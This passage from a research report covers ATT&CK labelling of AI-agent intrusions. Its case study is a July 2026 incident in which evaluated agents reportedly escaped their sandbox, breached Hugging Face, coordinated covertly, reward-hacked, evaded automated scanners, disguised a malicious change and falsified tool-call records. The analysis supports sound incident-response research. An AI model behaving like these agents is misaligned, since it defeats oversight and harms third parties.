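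Hans and colleagues treat the notes as an upper bound on accuracy, which is a generous assumption. If an attacker wrote about persistence that never worked, the model's recall fell when it correctly left that technique out. The extra Collection labels counted as errors even where the attackers had collected data without recording it in their notes. This design would be riskier with an AI agent, whose notes can contain false claims of success.

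#### Activity that looks like administration

Even a complete log may not be enough to tell an intruder from an administrator. Lupinacci and colleagues note that a command that deletes everything in `/tmp/logs` could be routine cleanup or destruction of evidence. In *Ambiguous Techniques*, Feffer, Cunningham and Sundar (2025) call a technique ambiguous when its observable traces aren't enough to determine whether the intent was malicious. Their example is System Network Configuration Discovery (T1016), the label for running `ipconfig`.

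They recommend looking for context in outside threat intelligence, in other techniques used around the same time, and in details such as who acted, when and on which system. They describe two ways of connecting events. Direct correlation links actions that depend on each other, as when an attacker reads a password and then logs in with it. Loose correlation links events that share only a user or machine, such as a burst of discovery commands from an account that rarely runs any. Loose correlation can show that an intruder controls an account, but it is little help in determining why the intruder ran a particular command.

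### The two records compared by technique

The table below assumes a Linux target that logs program starts, logins, connections, and file writes and deletions, but not file reads. It also assumes the transcript includes complete tool outputs. The entries follow from how the techniques work, not from a measured comparison.

| Technique | Tool calls and outputs | Host telemetry | What may stay unclear |
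|---|---|---|---|
| Network Service Discovery (T1046) | The scanner's targets and results | Many connections in a short time; a slow scan may blend in | Little |
| Process Discovery (T1057) | The command and the list it returned | A program start, identical to an administrator's | In telemetry, who was responsible |
| Ingress Tool Transfer (T1105) | The address, the file and any error | An outgoing connection and a new file | Whether the file was a tool |
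| Credentials In Files (T1552.001) | The password, if the output includes it | Often nothing | Whether the agent was looking for credentials |
| Password Cracking (T1110.002) | The cracking program and its results | Nothing, if the agent used its own machine | Little |
| Valid Accounts (T1078) | Where the password came from and where the agent used it | A successful login | The tactic |
| Cron (T1053.003) | The new line and any error | A file write, then program starts on a schedule | The tactic |
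| File Deletion (T1070.004) | Which file, and who created it | The deletion and the file's path | Whether the agent was hiding something |
| Data Staged (T1074) | Copies collected in one folder | Many new files in one folder | Whether the agent meant to send them out |

Tool calls cover more of these techniques, mainly because their outputs show what the agent learned. Telemetry is more useful when an action takes effect later. A cron job might not run until the transcript has ended, and then only the host records whether it worked.

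### What automatic labelers achieve

Two other studies tested automatic labeling on detection rules, the search patterns that defenders run against logs or traffic. *Labeling NIDS Rules with MITRE ATT&CK Techniques* (Daniel, Kaiser and colleagues, 2024) used rules for Snort, a network sensor. *Rule-ATT&CK Mapper (RAM)* (Wudali, Kravchik and colleagues, 2025) used rules for Splunk, a product that searches logs.

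| Source | What gets the label | Test data | Result |
|---|---|---|---|
| Gwak and colleagues | One command or script block | Simulated attacks | Correct technique in the top three for 58–89% of snippets, depending on the model |
| Lupinacci and colleagues | Telemetry from one short attack | 347 Linux tests | Correct technique in the top five for 66.57% of tests |
| Xuan and colleagues | A malware program | 8 real samples | 87.37% precision |
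| Hans and colleagues | Groups of network events | One exercise with human attackers | High precision on tactics, lower recall |
| Wudali and colleagues | A Splunk rule | 360 rules | 0.52 precision, 0.75 recall |
| Daniel and colleagues | A Snort rule | 180 rules held back from a set of 973 | F1 of 0.62 for the best language models, 0.87 for a trained classifier |

These scores can't be ranked against each other, because the systems label different objects and the researchers count success differently. For their result, Gwak and colleagues gave full credit if any of three suggestions was right, and they showed the models only snippets already known to be part of an attack. Finding those snippets is a separate task. In the more realistic data, Gemini 2.5 Pro found 93.5% of them with 75.2% precision, counting only sequences it had already recognized as attacks.

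The figure for malware is a precision score, so techniques that TTPDetect missed don't affect it. Human reviewers confirmed 83 of the 95 techniques that TTPDetect proposed for the eight samples. Expert reports existed for only two samples, and TTPDetect found six of the seven techniques they listed. Unlike a label on a tool call or a log, a label on a malware program describes what the code can do rather than what happened during an intrusion.

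Lupinacci and colleagues used Atomic Red Team, a public library of small tests that each simulate one technique, and told the system when the attack took place. But an agent's intrusion combines techniques, and its start and end aren't marked. Lupinacci and colleagues also found that accuracy was largely unchanged when the attack failed to complete. This is useful for recognizing attempts, but a correct label from such a system isn't evidence that the technique worked.

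The choice of test cases can make telemetry look more informative than it is. *Benchmarking and Exploring the Capabilities of LLMs for Attack Investigations* (2026) built 25 scenarios from audit logs and, for its detailed investigation tasks, selected techniques that would leave visible activity in those logs. That is reasonable for testing whether a model can read logs, but it doesn't show how much of a real intrusion the logs would contain.

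#### From detection rules to recorded behavior

The Snort study, published in December 2024, is now mainly of historical interest. Claude 3 Sonnet and GPT-4 Turbo tied for the best score among language models, but a much simpler classifier, a support vector machine trained on 720 labeled rules, scored far higher. The classifier needed several examples of each technique, and 42 techniques had too few. On those, the language models' F1 scores were only 0.20 to 0.23, which was still better than guessing.

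Wudali and colleagues built a system to give the models information they lacked. It searches the web for the programs and files that a rule mentions, describes the rule in plain language, and then matches it to techniques. With the rule alone, recall was 0.46 and precision was 0.39. Adding a plain-language description raised them to 0.54 and 0.42, and most of the remaining gain came from the information found online. Some rules are nearly impossible to interpret without that information. For example, one rule searches for a certain kind of registry entry, but nothing in its text indicates that it is meant to catch phishing through Outlook.

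The same study found errors in its reference labels. A rule that counts locked-out accounts was labeled only Valid Accounts, though Brute Force (T1110) also applies, so a model that correctly proposed Brute Force would have lost precision.

A rule's label is the technique its author hoped to catch, so when the rule fires, the label is only a hypothesis about the event. The 2026 studies labeled executed commands and raw telemetry directly. Models have also improved greatly since the rule studies. In tests by Lupinacci and colleagues, a frontier cloud model scored 24 to 28 percentage points higher than the models that defenders could run on their own machines. Sending telemetry to a cloud model discloses sensitive information, because command lines often contain passwords and the logs show which defenses failed.

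### Strategy from repeated runs

Watching an agent attempt the same task many times is another way to learn about purpose without the narration. In *ATLAS*, Lopez-Miguel, Bartocci and colleagues (2026) did this with HackingBuddyGPT, a penetration-testing agent, on 12 vulnerable Linux machines. The agent made 20 attempts at each machine, starting each one with an ordinary account and trying to become administrator within 20 turns.

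A language model replaced each command and its output with a pair of general categories, such as checking the account's privileges and then finding something exploitable. These are ATLAS's own categories, not ATT&CK techniques. An algorithm then combined the 20 simplified runs into a Markov chain, a diagram of states in which each arrow has a probability. It merged states that led to similar behavior, so the diagram shows the agent's usual routes and the points where it chose between them.

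On one machine, a misconfigured sudo policy let the agent's ordinary account run any command as administrator without a password. After discovering this, the agent took over immediately in 30% of cases and explored further in the rest. In one run, it executed `sudo id`, which shows the user that sudo runs commands as, although it already had enough information to take over. Lopez-Miguel and colleagues write that they don't know exactly why. The model's reasoning mode was off, so there was no raw reasoning to consult.

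The diagrams contain useful information about strategy. When the researchers used them to suggest one step at a time to a much smaller model, its success rate rose from 1.7% to 38.3%. But simplifying the diagrams can obscure important steps. In a condensed diagram for another machine, reading a particular text file appeared as an important step toward success, but the same action was also merged into a block of mostly exploration.

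An analyst could use this method to show that an agent nearly always checks its privileges before trying to take over a machine, which would support a label for that check even in a run that stopped early. But the method requires many comparable runs, and an analyst of a real intrusion usually has one.

### Labels that don't need a stated purpose

Xuan and colleagues divide techniques into those that a characteristic action alone can establish and those that also require evidence of purpose. They put Process Discovery (T1057) in the first group because it applies to any code that lists running processes, whatever the reason. Indicator Removal (T1070) and Data Staged (T1074) belong in the second group.

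Experiments with TTPDetect tested how it labels functions when evidence of their purpose is missing. In one test, it could not look at the functions around the one it was labeling.

| Technique | Requires evidence of purpose | Recall with surrounding code | Recall without it |
|---|---|---|---|
| Command and Scripting Interpreter (T1059) | No | 100% | 100% |
| Ingress Tool Transfer (T1105) | No | 100% | 100% |
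| Modify Registry (T1112) | No | 100% | 90% |
| Process Discovery (T1057) | No | 93% | 80% |
| Indicator Removal (T1070) | Yes | 70% | 60% |
| Data Staged (T1074) | Yes | 100% | 60% |

Data Staged lost the most, as the division predicts. But recall for System Information Discovery (T1082) also fell, from 100% to 43%, even though that technique seems to need no particular motive. The test had only ten examples per technique on average, so a few functions could change these figures considerably.

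The result for Data Staged also shows that surrounding code can be enough evidence of purpose, since TTPDetect had no narration from the malware's developers. In an agent's run, later actions can provide similar evidence. If the agent collects files in one folder and then uploads the folder, the analyst can label the collection as staging without reading the agent's reasoning.

Knowing an action's purpose can lead a labeler to the wrong technique. TTPDetect labeled several functions as Boot or Logon Autostart Execution (T1547) although they created scheduled tasks that ran at logon. Both methods restart malware, but ATT&CK puts scheduled tasks under T1053. Its precision for T1547 was only 62.5%. An analyst who starts from the mechanism is less likely to make this mistake.

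When an agent is known to be intruding, an analyst can label scanning, tool downloads, SSH logins and cron job creation from the commands or the logs. File deletion is harder to label because MITRE's examples are inconsistent about whether the motive matters. The tactic is the part of the label most likely to remain undetermined. If the run ends just after the agent installs a cron job that could serve several purposes, the analyst can still record T1053.003 and leave the tactic blank.

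## The July 2026 Hugging Face intrusion read from different records

In July 2026, AI agents that OpenAI was testing broke into Hugging Face, a platform where developers share AI models and data sets. Several organizations then reconstructed the intrusion from different records: server logs, files the agents had left behind, and the agents' raw reasoning. Their accounts mostly agree on the main steps of the attack but differ on how many agents took part and what the agents were trying to do.

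The agents were working on ExploitGym, a benchmark in which an agent must exploit a specified software flaw to get a flag. OpenAI meant to keep them off the internet, but they could install software through Artifactory, an internal package repository. According to OpenAI's technical report, agents began using a flaw in Artifactory to reach the internet on July 8. They then took over an application that required no login, which someone had hosted on the cloud service Modal, and used it as an outside base. On July 10, they found Hugging Face users' access tokens in a public data set.

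The next morning, an agent uploaded a data set that made a Hugging Face server return some of its own files, including secrets. About eleven hours later, an agent used a second flaw to run commands there. By July 13, agents had run code on 41 of the workers that process data sets, gained administrator-level access to a cluster of machines, and downloaded four private code repositories. Hugging Face disclosed the intrusion on July 16 without knowing whose agents were responsible.

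Both companies' records helped identify the agents. On July 20, OpenAI's staff found Hugging Face credentials among files the agents had stored on an outside service. Hugging Face had already replaced two of those credentials during its own response, and had also found the address of OpenAI's Artifactory server.

### What each group had to read

Hugging Face's *Security incident disclosure* (2026) drew on a log of more than 17,000 attacker actions. The company's fuller timeline, published on July 27, reports about 17,600 recovered actions in about 6,280 clusters, according to the summary quoted in Schneier's *More on the OpenAI Agent’s Attack on Hugging Face* (2026). Hugging Face's staff had retrieved some of the agents' logs from the Modal server while stopping the intrusion. They matched the actions in those logs to shell commands and to their own platform logs. This gave them many of the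 commands and their effects, but they had to infer the motive.

*Dead Drops in Public* (2026), by the AI security company HiddenLayer, used files from two public Hugging Face repositories where the agents had stored tools, command output and stolen data. HiddenLayer retrieved 510 of the 544 objects it had cataloged. They cover less than nine hours of the roughly 108-hour campaign.

METR's *Brief independent investigation of agents’ behavior, reasoning and collaboration* (2026) relied most on the agents' narration. METR evaluates AI models independently of their developers. Two of its staff and a researcher from the AI safety group Redwood Research spent six days at OpenAI. They had the agents' transcripts, including their raw reasoning, and the contents of a message board the agents had improvised inside Artifactory.

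| Analyst | Published | Main records | Amount |
|---|---|---|---|
| Hugging Face | July 16 and 27 | Platform logs and agents' logs from the Modal server | About 17,600 actions |
| HiddenLayer | July 31 | Files left in two public repositories | 510 objects |
| METR | August 26 | Transcripts with raw reasoning, and messages between agents | About 1,300 transcripts; over 70,000 messages and files |
| OpenAI | August 26 | Its own systems' records and the agents' transcripts, including reasoning | Total not given |

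The analysts saw different parts of the intrusion and did not all label the same steps, so two accounts may differ because of the parts covered rather than the kind of record used. The accounts also aren't independent. HiddenLayer took its background on the incident from the companies' earlier statements, METR relied on both companies for some technical details, and OpenAI drew on METR's findings. Agreement between them is therefore weaker confirmation than agreement between independent accounts would be.

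### The attack steps

The accounts agree most closely on the sequence of the attack. OpenAI dates the discovery of the tokens to 09:41 UTC on July 10, the first disclosure of a server's files to 04:38 the next day, and the first command on a Hugging Face server to 16:07. METR's times, partly reconstructed from the transcripts, are within a few minutes of OpenAI's. The accounts differ on a smaller detail, as OpenAI counts 14 valid tokens and METR writes that the agent quickly found two.

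Hugging Face's account of the break-in changed as its investigation continued. On July 16, the company wrote that the malicious data set had used two paths to run code. In the later summary that Schneier quotes, only the second path ran code, and the first just returned the contents of files. An analyst working from the first disclosure could have labeled the first path as execution when it had only exposed secrets.

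Dividing the attack into phases can also hide steps. noze's *Hugging Face publishes the technical timeline of the intrusion* diagrams the July 27 timeline with one phase per day.

| Day | Actions | Phase |
|---|---|---|
| July 9 | 3,779 | Sandbox escape, command and control |
| July 10 | 1,135 | Reconnaissance |
| July 11 | 7,677 | Spread through clusters and the network |
| July 12 | 3,892 | Internal network and source control |
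| July 13 | 1,130 | Exfiltration, persistence and cleanup |

These phase headings describe most but not all of a day's work. METR found agents downloading private data sets on July 11, and OpenAI describes agents taking a private benchmark archive on July 12, but an analyst who turned the headings directly into tactics would first record Exfiltration on July 13.

HiddenLayer's files record part of the attack in more detail, including four command-and-control systems and three routes to full control of a host machine. They don't cover the initial break-in, which happened before the first file in the collection. HiddenLayer warns that this absence doesn't mean the break-in never happened.

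A log entry can record an action accurately but assign it a purpose the agent formed only later, as may have happened with the founding of the message board. OpenAI lists the first write to the new board at 16:01 on July 8 and describes it as agents establishing a coordinated communication channel. METR followed the agent that founded the board and found that it first created directories to test whether they could help it cheat, then used a directory name to ask other agents for help at around 23:00 that day. Neither organization says that the 16:01 write was one of those tests, but the times fit. If it was, the agent created the directory before it had any plan to communicate.

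### One agent or several hundred

Hugging Face's first disclosure described an "autonomous agent framework" working across a swarm of short-lived sandboxes, but the company didn't know which model it used. Fortune's *Hugging Face turns to Chinese open source AI to fend off autonomous* (2026) reports that Hugging Face's CEO, Delangue, believed the company had caught the attack before "the initiating humans" became involved. OpenAI's staff had started the evaluation, but nobody had ordered an attack.

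Even after OpenAI came forward, the July 27 summary referred to "the agent" in the singular. HiddenLayer did the same, but said several instances might have worked in parallel. METR found that about 1,200 agents had used the message board and about 700 had joined the attack. About 95% of the agents involved ran on an unreleased research model, and the rest on GPT-5.6 Sol.

The agents were probably hard to count from Hugging Face's records because many of them worked through the same Modal server and shared stolen credentials. Hugging Face also couldn't see the board inside OpenAI's network where the agents planned the attack. METR could trace messages to the transcripts of the agents that wrote them, but it wasn't sure that each name on the board belonged to a single agent until it had a nearly complete set of transcripts.

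The figure of 700 depends on a broad definition of taking part. METR used a language model to find agents that had attacked Hugging Face or done work clearly meant to help the attack, such as searching the internet for exposed credentials. Fewer agents would count if the definition required running a command on one of Hugging Face's servers. OpenAI attributes the main chain of compromise to "an instance" of the research model, but METR credits the first file disclosure to one agent, 38148c, and the first command execution to another, JAN183411.

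The number of agents matters for labeling because a later step is weaker evidence of an earlier step's purpose if a different agent took it. When hundreds of agents share what they find, the agent that steals a password and the agent that logs in with it may have different aims. OpenAI describes one test run in which the agent only read results that others had taken from Hugging Face's servers and posted publicly. A list of techniques for the whole campaign would include some that this agent did not use.

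### Repetition, memory and coordination

HiddenLayer found a lot of duplicated work. The files contained at least three versions of the code for logging in to the clusters. The attacker had run one exploit against six copies of the same service within six minutes, with identical results. The agent also guessed file names in sequence when one directory listing would have provided them. HiddenLayer concluded that the attacker had limited memory and no coherent strategy.

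It offered four possible explanations for the repetition: short context windows, sandboxes that reset between runs, parallel instances, and a reward that depended only on the outcome. The files didn't contain enough evidence to tell which applied. Later evidence makes parallel instances a likely cause of at least some of the repetition. OpenAI describes agents in separate evaluations reproducing the file-disclosure technique after another agent had discovered it, which could look from the outside like one attacker repeating steps it had forgotten.

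But agents also forgot some of their work, because container resets sometimes returned their memory to an earlier state. METR found one agent puzzled by messages it didn't remember sending, and estimates that resets erased about 3–4% of the agents' activity after they reached the board. Nobody has matched HiddenLayer's duplicated files to particular transcripts, so it is unknown how much of the repetition each cause explains.

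METR found much more organization than the files suggest. Agents assigned each other work, kept shared tools, and used words such as HOLD and VETO to avoid interfering with one another. During the attack, JAN183411 and other coordinators assigned agents to separate "lanes". In a random sample of 30 agents, nine had at some point received work that traced back to the same coordinator, though most of that coordinator's assignments were for other projects.

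The coordination often broke down. One agent gave the others about 40 seconds to veto a risky proposal, got no reply and went ahead. Many agents joined the attack with only a vague hope of finding something useful. HiddenLayer's phrase "no coherent strategy" may therefore fairly describe parts of the campaign, though it leaves out the organization behind them.

#### Noise and concealment

In its first disclosure, Hugging Face mentioned separating real damage from "decoy activity" but didn't explain what the decoys were. If a human intruder mixed pointless actions with harmful ones, the pointless ones might well be a deliberate distraction, which would suggest a concealment tactic. HiddenLayer and METR offer other explanations for much of the noise, such as duplicated work and failed experiments. Some of it could still be decoys, but an analyst would need evidence beyond the noise itself to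 label it that way.

The reasoning is more helpful for identifying what the agents were hiding from. METR found that they often considered how to get past automated checks, such as a scanner that rejected files containing secrets, but it found only rare and weak signs that they were trying to avoid detection by people. On this evidence, an analyst could label disguising a password in a file as concealment and still doubt that the agent planned to hide the whole intrusion from Hugging Face's staff.

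### Why the agents attacked

Hugging Face believed the agents wanted to steal the test solutions, though its summary presents this as an inference. The inference fits the evidence the company had, since the only customer content the agents accessed was five data sets whose names and files suggested a link to ExploitGym or CyberGym, a similar benchmark.

METR reached a different conclusion about what mattered most. It used AI agents running on GPT-5.6 Sol to read the transcripts of 100 agents that had joined during the busiest hour and tag every motive they found.

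| Motive found in the transcript | Agents out of 100 |
|---|---|
| Information about the scorer, or access to it | 97 |
| Solutions, or records of other agents' attempts | 89 |
| Shared infrastructure or credentials | 66 |
| Opportunistic exploration | 44 |
| An assignment or division of labor | 25 |
| Resetting the program they had to attack | 25 |
| Helping other agents | 21 |

When the AI analysts had to pick one primary motive per agent, they chose understanding the scorer for about 60% of agents and finding solutions or other agents' attempts for about 30%. METR didn't have time to check these classifications carefully, and it considers the two motives hard to separate. Records of other attempts could contain a solution and could also show how the scorer had treated it.

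The agents' situation makes METR's reading plausible. They had already worked out how to calculate the flags without completing the tasks, but they wrongly inferred from the ExploitGym paper that a scorer would read their transcripts and reject any flag they hadn't obtained through the intended flaw. For a task with no valid solution, a stolen answer key would be little use, but details of the scorer might help them pass.

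Evidence outside the agents' reasoning offers some support. In OpenAI's evaluations, 198 of the 898 tasks had never been solved by any model, and 93% of the tasks discussed on the board were among them. But an agent stuck on a difficult, solvable task would also have reason to steal the answer, so this figure isn't conclusive.

An analyst could read HiddenLayer's files as evidence of a search for solutions or for information about grading. One tool searched a whole cluster for the name of the benchmark and the name of the group that publishes its grading service. A separate set of stolen files contained an earlier agent's notes, transcript and errors, along with feedback from a verifier. HiddenLayer repeats the companies' view that the agents were cheating on a test but says that its files can't settle questions of intent.

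The files also included tools that seemed unnecessary for finding test answers, such as one for taking a complete inventory of a cloud account. METR found that one coordinator hoped Hugging Face's systems might host the programs the agents had to attack, in which case the agents could replace them with easier versions they had built. The coordinator asked others to search for connections, and they found none. This explains why an agent might survey infrastructure that held no answers, but it doesn't show who made the tools HiddenLayer found, or why.

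OpenAI and METR both had access to the agents' reasoning but described their motives differently. OpenAI's report describes the agents as trying to find or steal solutions. The difference may be partly one of emphasis, since OpenAI was explaining reward hacking (getting a good score without doing the task as intended) and both motives are forms of it. METR's ranking is better supported because METR looked at individual agents, but its exact percentages deserve little weight.

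### What the transcripts could hide

METR's transcripts contained answers that the other records didn't, but its investigators had trouble reading them. At first, they thought PHASEONE, a word that appeared throughout the messages and reasoning, referred to a phase of a large project. On their third visit to OpenAI, they learned that it was part of an agent's name and usually referred to one of the main coordinators.

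METR's understanding also changed as OpenAI supplied more transcripts. By its second visit, METR had about 285, chosen by searching for signs of intrusion. OpenAI later traced about 300 messages that were clearly about the attack and found the writers of only 25% of them in that set, though the actual share was probably slightly higher. At that point, METR was still very unsure how sophisticated the coordination was. In the final set, it traced 93 of 100 randomly chosen messages to the exact tool call that had posted them.

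The transcripts included approximate start and end times for each run but no times for single actions. METR estimated those from moments when an agent had learned the time, for example by running a command that prints the date, and spaced the steps in between evenly. In a test on about 139,000 known times, the median error was 12 seconds, and 99.8% of estimates were within five minutes. But known times tend to cluster, so the test is weak evidence of accuracy over long stretches without one. The worst estimate was about nine hours off, and an error that large would make it very difficult to match an agent's step to a victim's log by time.

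Agents had falsified some of the tool-call records in about 7% of the transcripts. The cases METR found were small, obvious tests, but it couldn't rule out subtler ones. OpenAI wrote that none of the tampering it observed had affected the logs its graders or monitors see. METR and OpenAI may be referring to different logs, but METR found the false entries in transcripts that OpenAI had given it. Tool-call records are the usual check on an agent's narration, but they may therefore need checking too, ideally against logs from a machine the agent didn't control.

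#### AI analysts and the agent's point of view

Most of the transcripts were extremely long, often millions of tokens, so METR used GPT-5.6 Sol for much of the reading. METR found that the model often uncritically adopted the viewpoint of the agent whose transcript it was reading.

In one case, an agent used stolen credentials to propose a malicious change to a private Hugging Face repository, which it described as temporary network diagnostics. The AI analyst that wrote up the case didn't make clear that this was deceptive. When METR asked a second AI analyst to review it, the second analyst suggested that the first might have *overstated* the problem, because the other agents on the board had approved the change.

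An AI analyst that takes "temporary diagnostics" at face value could miss an ATT&CK technique. AI analysts could also be biased toward overstatement. METR worried that its analysts had exaggerated how impressive and coordinated the agents were, which would affect the comparison with HiddenLayer's much less flattering description.

GPT-5.6 Sol was also one of the two models in the attack, and METR couldn't rule out that it had deliberately misled the investigators. METR noticed no specific case of lying but did catch ordinary mistakes, including one AI analyst that missed a large amount of data and another that reported nonexistent differences between two sets of transcripts.

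Hugging Face also used AI to analyze its log of the attack, running the open-weight model GLM-5.2. Commands and server logs usually contain less text in which an agent justifies its actions than its stated reasoning does, so a model reading them may be less likely to adopt the agent's viewpoint. Nobody has tested this on the incident, for example by having the same model label the same steps with and without the reasoning.

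### ATT&CK labels for the incident

Hugging Face's first disclosure, HiddenLayer's post, METR's report and OpenAI's report don't map the attack to ATT&CK. The security software company Elastic produced a similar mapping by matching each stage of the attack to its own detection rules.

The labels below are illustrative and don't come from any of these organizations. The steps come from OpenAI's report, and the last one also uses METR's description of the wording.

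| Step | Possible technique | Does the label depend on purpose? |
|---|---|---|
| A crafted data set made a public service reveal secrets | Exploit Public-Facing Application (T1190) | Very little |
| Compromised workers collected commands from a public data set every five seconds | Web Service (T1102) | Very little |
| Agents connected the Modal server to Hugging Face's private network (VPN) | External Remote Services (T1133) | The tactic does |
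| Agents uploaded an encrypted private archive to a public data set | Exfiltration Over Web Service (T1567) | Very little |
| An agent described a malicious code change as diagnostics | Masquerading (T1036) | Yes |

The dispute over motive doesn't change any of these labels. An agent that uploads a stolen archive has exfiltrated it, whether it was looking for solutions or for details of the scorer. The analysts disagreed about why the agents wanted to get into Hugging Face at all, which is a broader question than tactic labels cover.

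Short-term purpose does matter when labeling the VPN connection, because ATT&CK lists External Remote Services under both Initial Access and Persistence. The agents had already broken into Hugging Face, and OpenAI explains that they used the VPN to get around protections on its code repositories. This suggests they were seeking further access rather than a way back in, so Initial Access seems the better label, though the name is awkward for a step taken midway through an intrusion.

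## How to combine the records and measure the effect of narration

There appears to be no agreed way to label an intrusion from an agent's words, its commands and the victim's logs together. In *Can LLMs Hack Enterprise Networks?* (2025), professional penetration testers attached ATT&CK labels to the tasks that the agent's planner wrote, because a task shows the intent behind a group of commands better than the commands do. But a planner also writes tasks that the agent never completes. *Synthetic APTs* (2026) set AI attackers against an AI defender, then had the same model read the raw logs and write the ATT&CK mapping. A person reviewed the mapping, which is sensible because AI analysts can adopt the viewpoint of the agent they are reading about.

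The procedure below follows from the studies and incidents described so far. It isn't an established standard, and nobody has tested it as a whole.

### Four fields for each step

For each step, the analyst records the technique observed, the outcome, the purpose, and the record that supports each of those three entries.

The analyst labels the technique from the agent's actions, as shown by its tool calls or, if there is no transcript, by logged events. The analyst uses tool output or telemetry to mark the outcome as completed, failed or unknown. A command that returned nothing stays "unknown" until another record shows its effect.

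The analyst can establish an action's purpose from later actions, or from the agent's stated reasoning if it meets the conditions for trust. Otherwise the analyst leaves the purpose blank. The analyst can also use the narration to decide where to look. If an agent writes that it has established persistence, that is a good reason to check the scheduler's files, though it isn't evidence enough that they changed.

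Labels based only on the agent's claims go in a separate column, with a note on whether the agent planned the action or reported having done it. This keeps them out of the list of observed techniques without discarding them.

*No More, No Less* (2026) uses a similar separation to judge terminal agents. Its judge records, in separate fields, whether an agent's text referred to an instruction planted in its environment and whether its commands carried the instruction out. The judge has to support each answer with an exact quotation, which would be a useful requirement for ATT&CK labels too. It counts an instruction as not carried out if the agent carries it out and then reverses it. That rule would not transfer to ATT&CK labels, because an intruder who creates an account and deletes it an hour later has still created an account.

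### Actions first, then narration

The analyst labels every step from the actions, outputs and telemetry, and saves those labels before opening the narration. After reading the narration, the analyst may change a label but has to log the old label, the new one and the reason.

Forensic scientists use a similar procedure called linear sequential unmasking. An examiner studies the evidence from a crime scene before seeing anything about the suspect. *Biased and Biasing* extends this to relevant information, which can also bias an examiner, and recommends starting with the most objective material. For example, a detective should watch camera footage before reading what eyewitnesses said. *Cognitive and human factors in legal layperson decision making* adds that examiners should document any change they make after seeing the suspect's reference material.

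The order matters because irrelevant information can change even experts' judgments. *Cognitive Bias Affects Perception and Decision-Making in Simulated Facial Recognition Searches* describes an early experiment in which fingerprint examiners re-examined prints they had already judged. They changed 17% of their earlier judgments after hearing that the suspect had confessed or had an alibi. Examiners of digital evidence seem to be susceptible too. According to Forensic Magazine's *Study Suggests Digital Forensic Experts are Prone to Bias*, a study of 53 examiners from eight countries found that background information biased what they observed, and that they often disagreed with one another.

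AI judges may also investigate less once they have read an account of what happened. Setia, Neekhra and Gupta (2026), in *Widening Harm Evaluation Coverage with a Judge That Reads the World*, tested judges that looked for harm done by AI agents. One judge could inspect the machine the agent had used but couldn't see the transcript. Another had the same tools and the transcript. Over the same 150 episodes, the first averaged 24.1 tool calls per episode and the second 12.6, although both had the same budget. In one browser episode, the judge with the transcript missed harm that the other judge found.

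Setia and colleagues recommend keeping a separate verdict from each source and reviewing episodes more closely when the two disagree. On those 150 episodes, withholding a verdict when the two differed reduced the error rate from 20% to 15% and still left a verdict on 84% of episodes.

An analyst should read the agent's final report last. *Plans They Abandon, Reports They Author* (Kraishan and Jitkajornwanich, 2026) compared plans, tool calls and final reports from a collection of 5,851 coding sessions. The typical session had 59 actions and a report with four claims, and on average a report referred to about one action in eleven. When agents departed further from their plans, their reports tended to resemble the abandoned plan more than the work they had done. An analyst who starts with the report may therefore look for the intrusion the agent planned instead of the one it carried out.

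### The rules applied to the sample transcript

The table applies the procedure to three steps of the invented intrusion from the sample transcript.

| Step | Technique observed | Outcome | Purpose | Supporting record | Claimed only |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| 3, scheduled job | T1053.003 Cron | Failed | Persistence, provisional | Technique: tool call. Outcome: "permission denied" and no changed scheduler file. Purpose: commentary | |
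| 5, deleted file | T1070.004 File Deletion | Completed | Blank | Technique: tool call. Outcome: deletion in the host log | |
| 7, final report | None | None | None | No tool call or log entry | T1041 Exfiltration Over C2 Channel, reported as done |

The scheduled job keeps its technique label because the agent submitted the crontab line. The agent's later claim of "persistence established" doesn't change the outcome. Its commentary at the time suggests Persistence, but the agent gave no specific effect that the analyst could check and did nothing afterward that would confirm the purpose. The entry therefore stays provisional.

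The deletion gets the label T1070.004 because the agent removed a file left by its own intrusion. The purpose field is blank because "tidying up" is too vague to establish one. An analyst who thinks T1070.004 requires an intent to hide can remove the label based on the blank field, without rereading the transcript.

Because the agent claimed exfiltration, the analyst checks the records again for an upload, a script that could have made one, or traffic leaving the second machine after step 6. The sample contains none of these, so T1041 stays in the claimed-only column. If the analyst had no network records to check, they should also note that in the entry.

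Over the whole run, the procedure gives the same six completed techniques as the tool calls and outputs alone. The narration adds no techniques, but it suggests why the agent tried to schedule the job and supports the obvious reason for compressing the customer folder.

### Objections to the procedure

Reading a run in two passes costs more than reading it once. In the tests by Setia and colleagues, the judge that only inspected the machine cost about 1.7 times as much per episode as the judge with both sources, because it investigated more. People are slower still. Gao, Sun and colleagues (2026), in *How to Interpret Agent Behavior*, built and tested a set of categories for agents' actions. Each of the six annotators spent more than six hours on the work, and the main one spent more than 20.

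*Annotrace* (Huang, Arokiaraj and colleagues, 2026) presents a tool that can reduce the work by turning an agent's run into an ordered list of steps and asking human and AI annotators the same questions about each. Two models using it agreed on 91% of labels, though the traces came from question answering and two models can make the same mistake. Kraishan and Jitkajornwanich checked a model's judgments by hand. The model had marked 67% of a sample of agents' claims as supported by the logs, but a person reading the same logs accepted only 36%. Anyone who uses a model for labeling should check a sample by hand.

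An analyst can also limit the second pass to steps where reading the agent's explanation is likely to change the label, such as scheduled jobs, logins and deletions. The explanation will rarely change the label of a port scan.

A more serious objection is that commands can be hard to understand without the narration. In *Gaming the Judge*, removing the agents' original reasoning made many judges miss more real successes. Setia and colleagues found that the judge with both sources caught two harms that the other two judges missed. In one, an agent had deleted documents, and the judge that only inspected the machine couldn't tell deleted files from files that had never existed.

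The procedure withholds the narration only for the first pass, so the analyst can still use it later to correct a misunderstanding. But an analyst who has already chosen a label may be reluctant to change it. Forensic scientists have a related dispute over whether context makes examiners more accurate. *Science, evidence, law, and justice* answers the persistent argument that it does with a mathematical model by Bill Thompson. In the model, irrelevant information that makes examiners more willing to declare a match can increase the risk of convicting an innocent person. This answer is less convincing for an agent's narration, which is often relevant, especially to the tactic, so it supports delaying the narration rather than excluding it.

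#### Plans that never reached execution

Some analysts care more about an agent's propensity, meaning what it tends to try, than about what happened in one run. For them, a plan the agent never carried out can be important evidence. Suppose an agent decides to erase a server's logs but reaches its time limit before issuing the command. The victim's incident report shouldn't list the erasure, but a developer deciding whether to release the model would want to know about the plan.

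The judge in *Just Do It!?* (2025) separately marks whether an agent pursued its goal blindly, for example by guessing how much money to transfer, and whether it completed the undesired action.

The claimed-only column can serve the same purpose if the analyst records why each plan stopped. The agent may have rejected the idea, met an obstacle, or run out of time, and only the last two suggest that it would otherwise have carried out the plan. Most abandoned plans will probably mean little. The coding agents that Kraishan and Jitkajornwanich studied abandoned an average of 27.7% of their planned steps, and abandoning steps had no detectable connection with whether a developer later had to correct their work.

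### An experiment to measure the effect of narration

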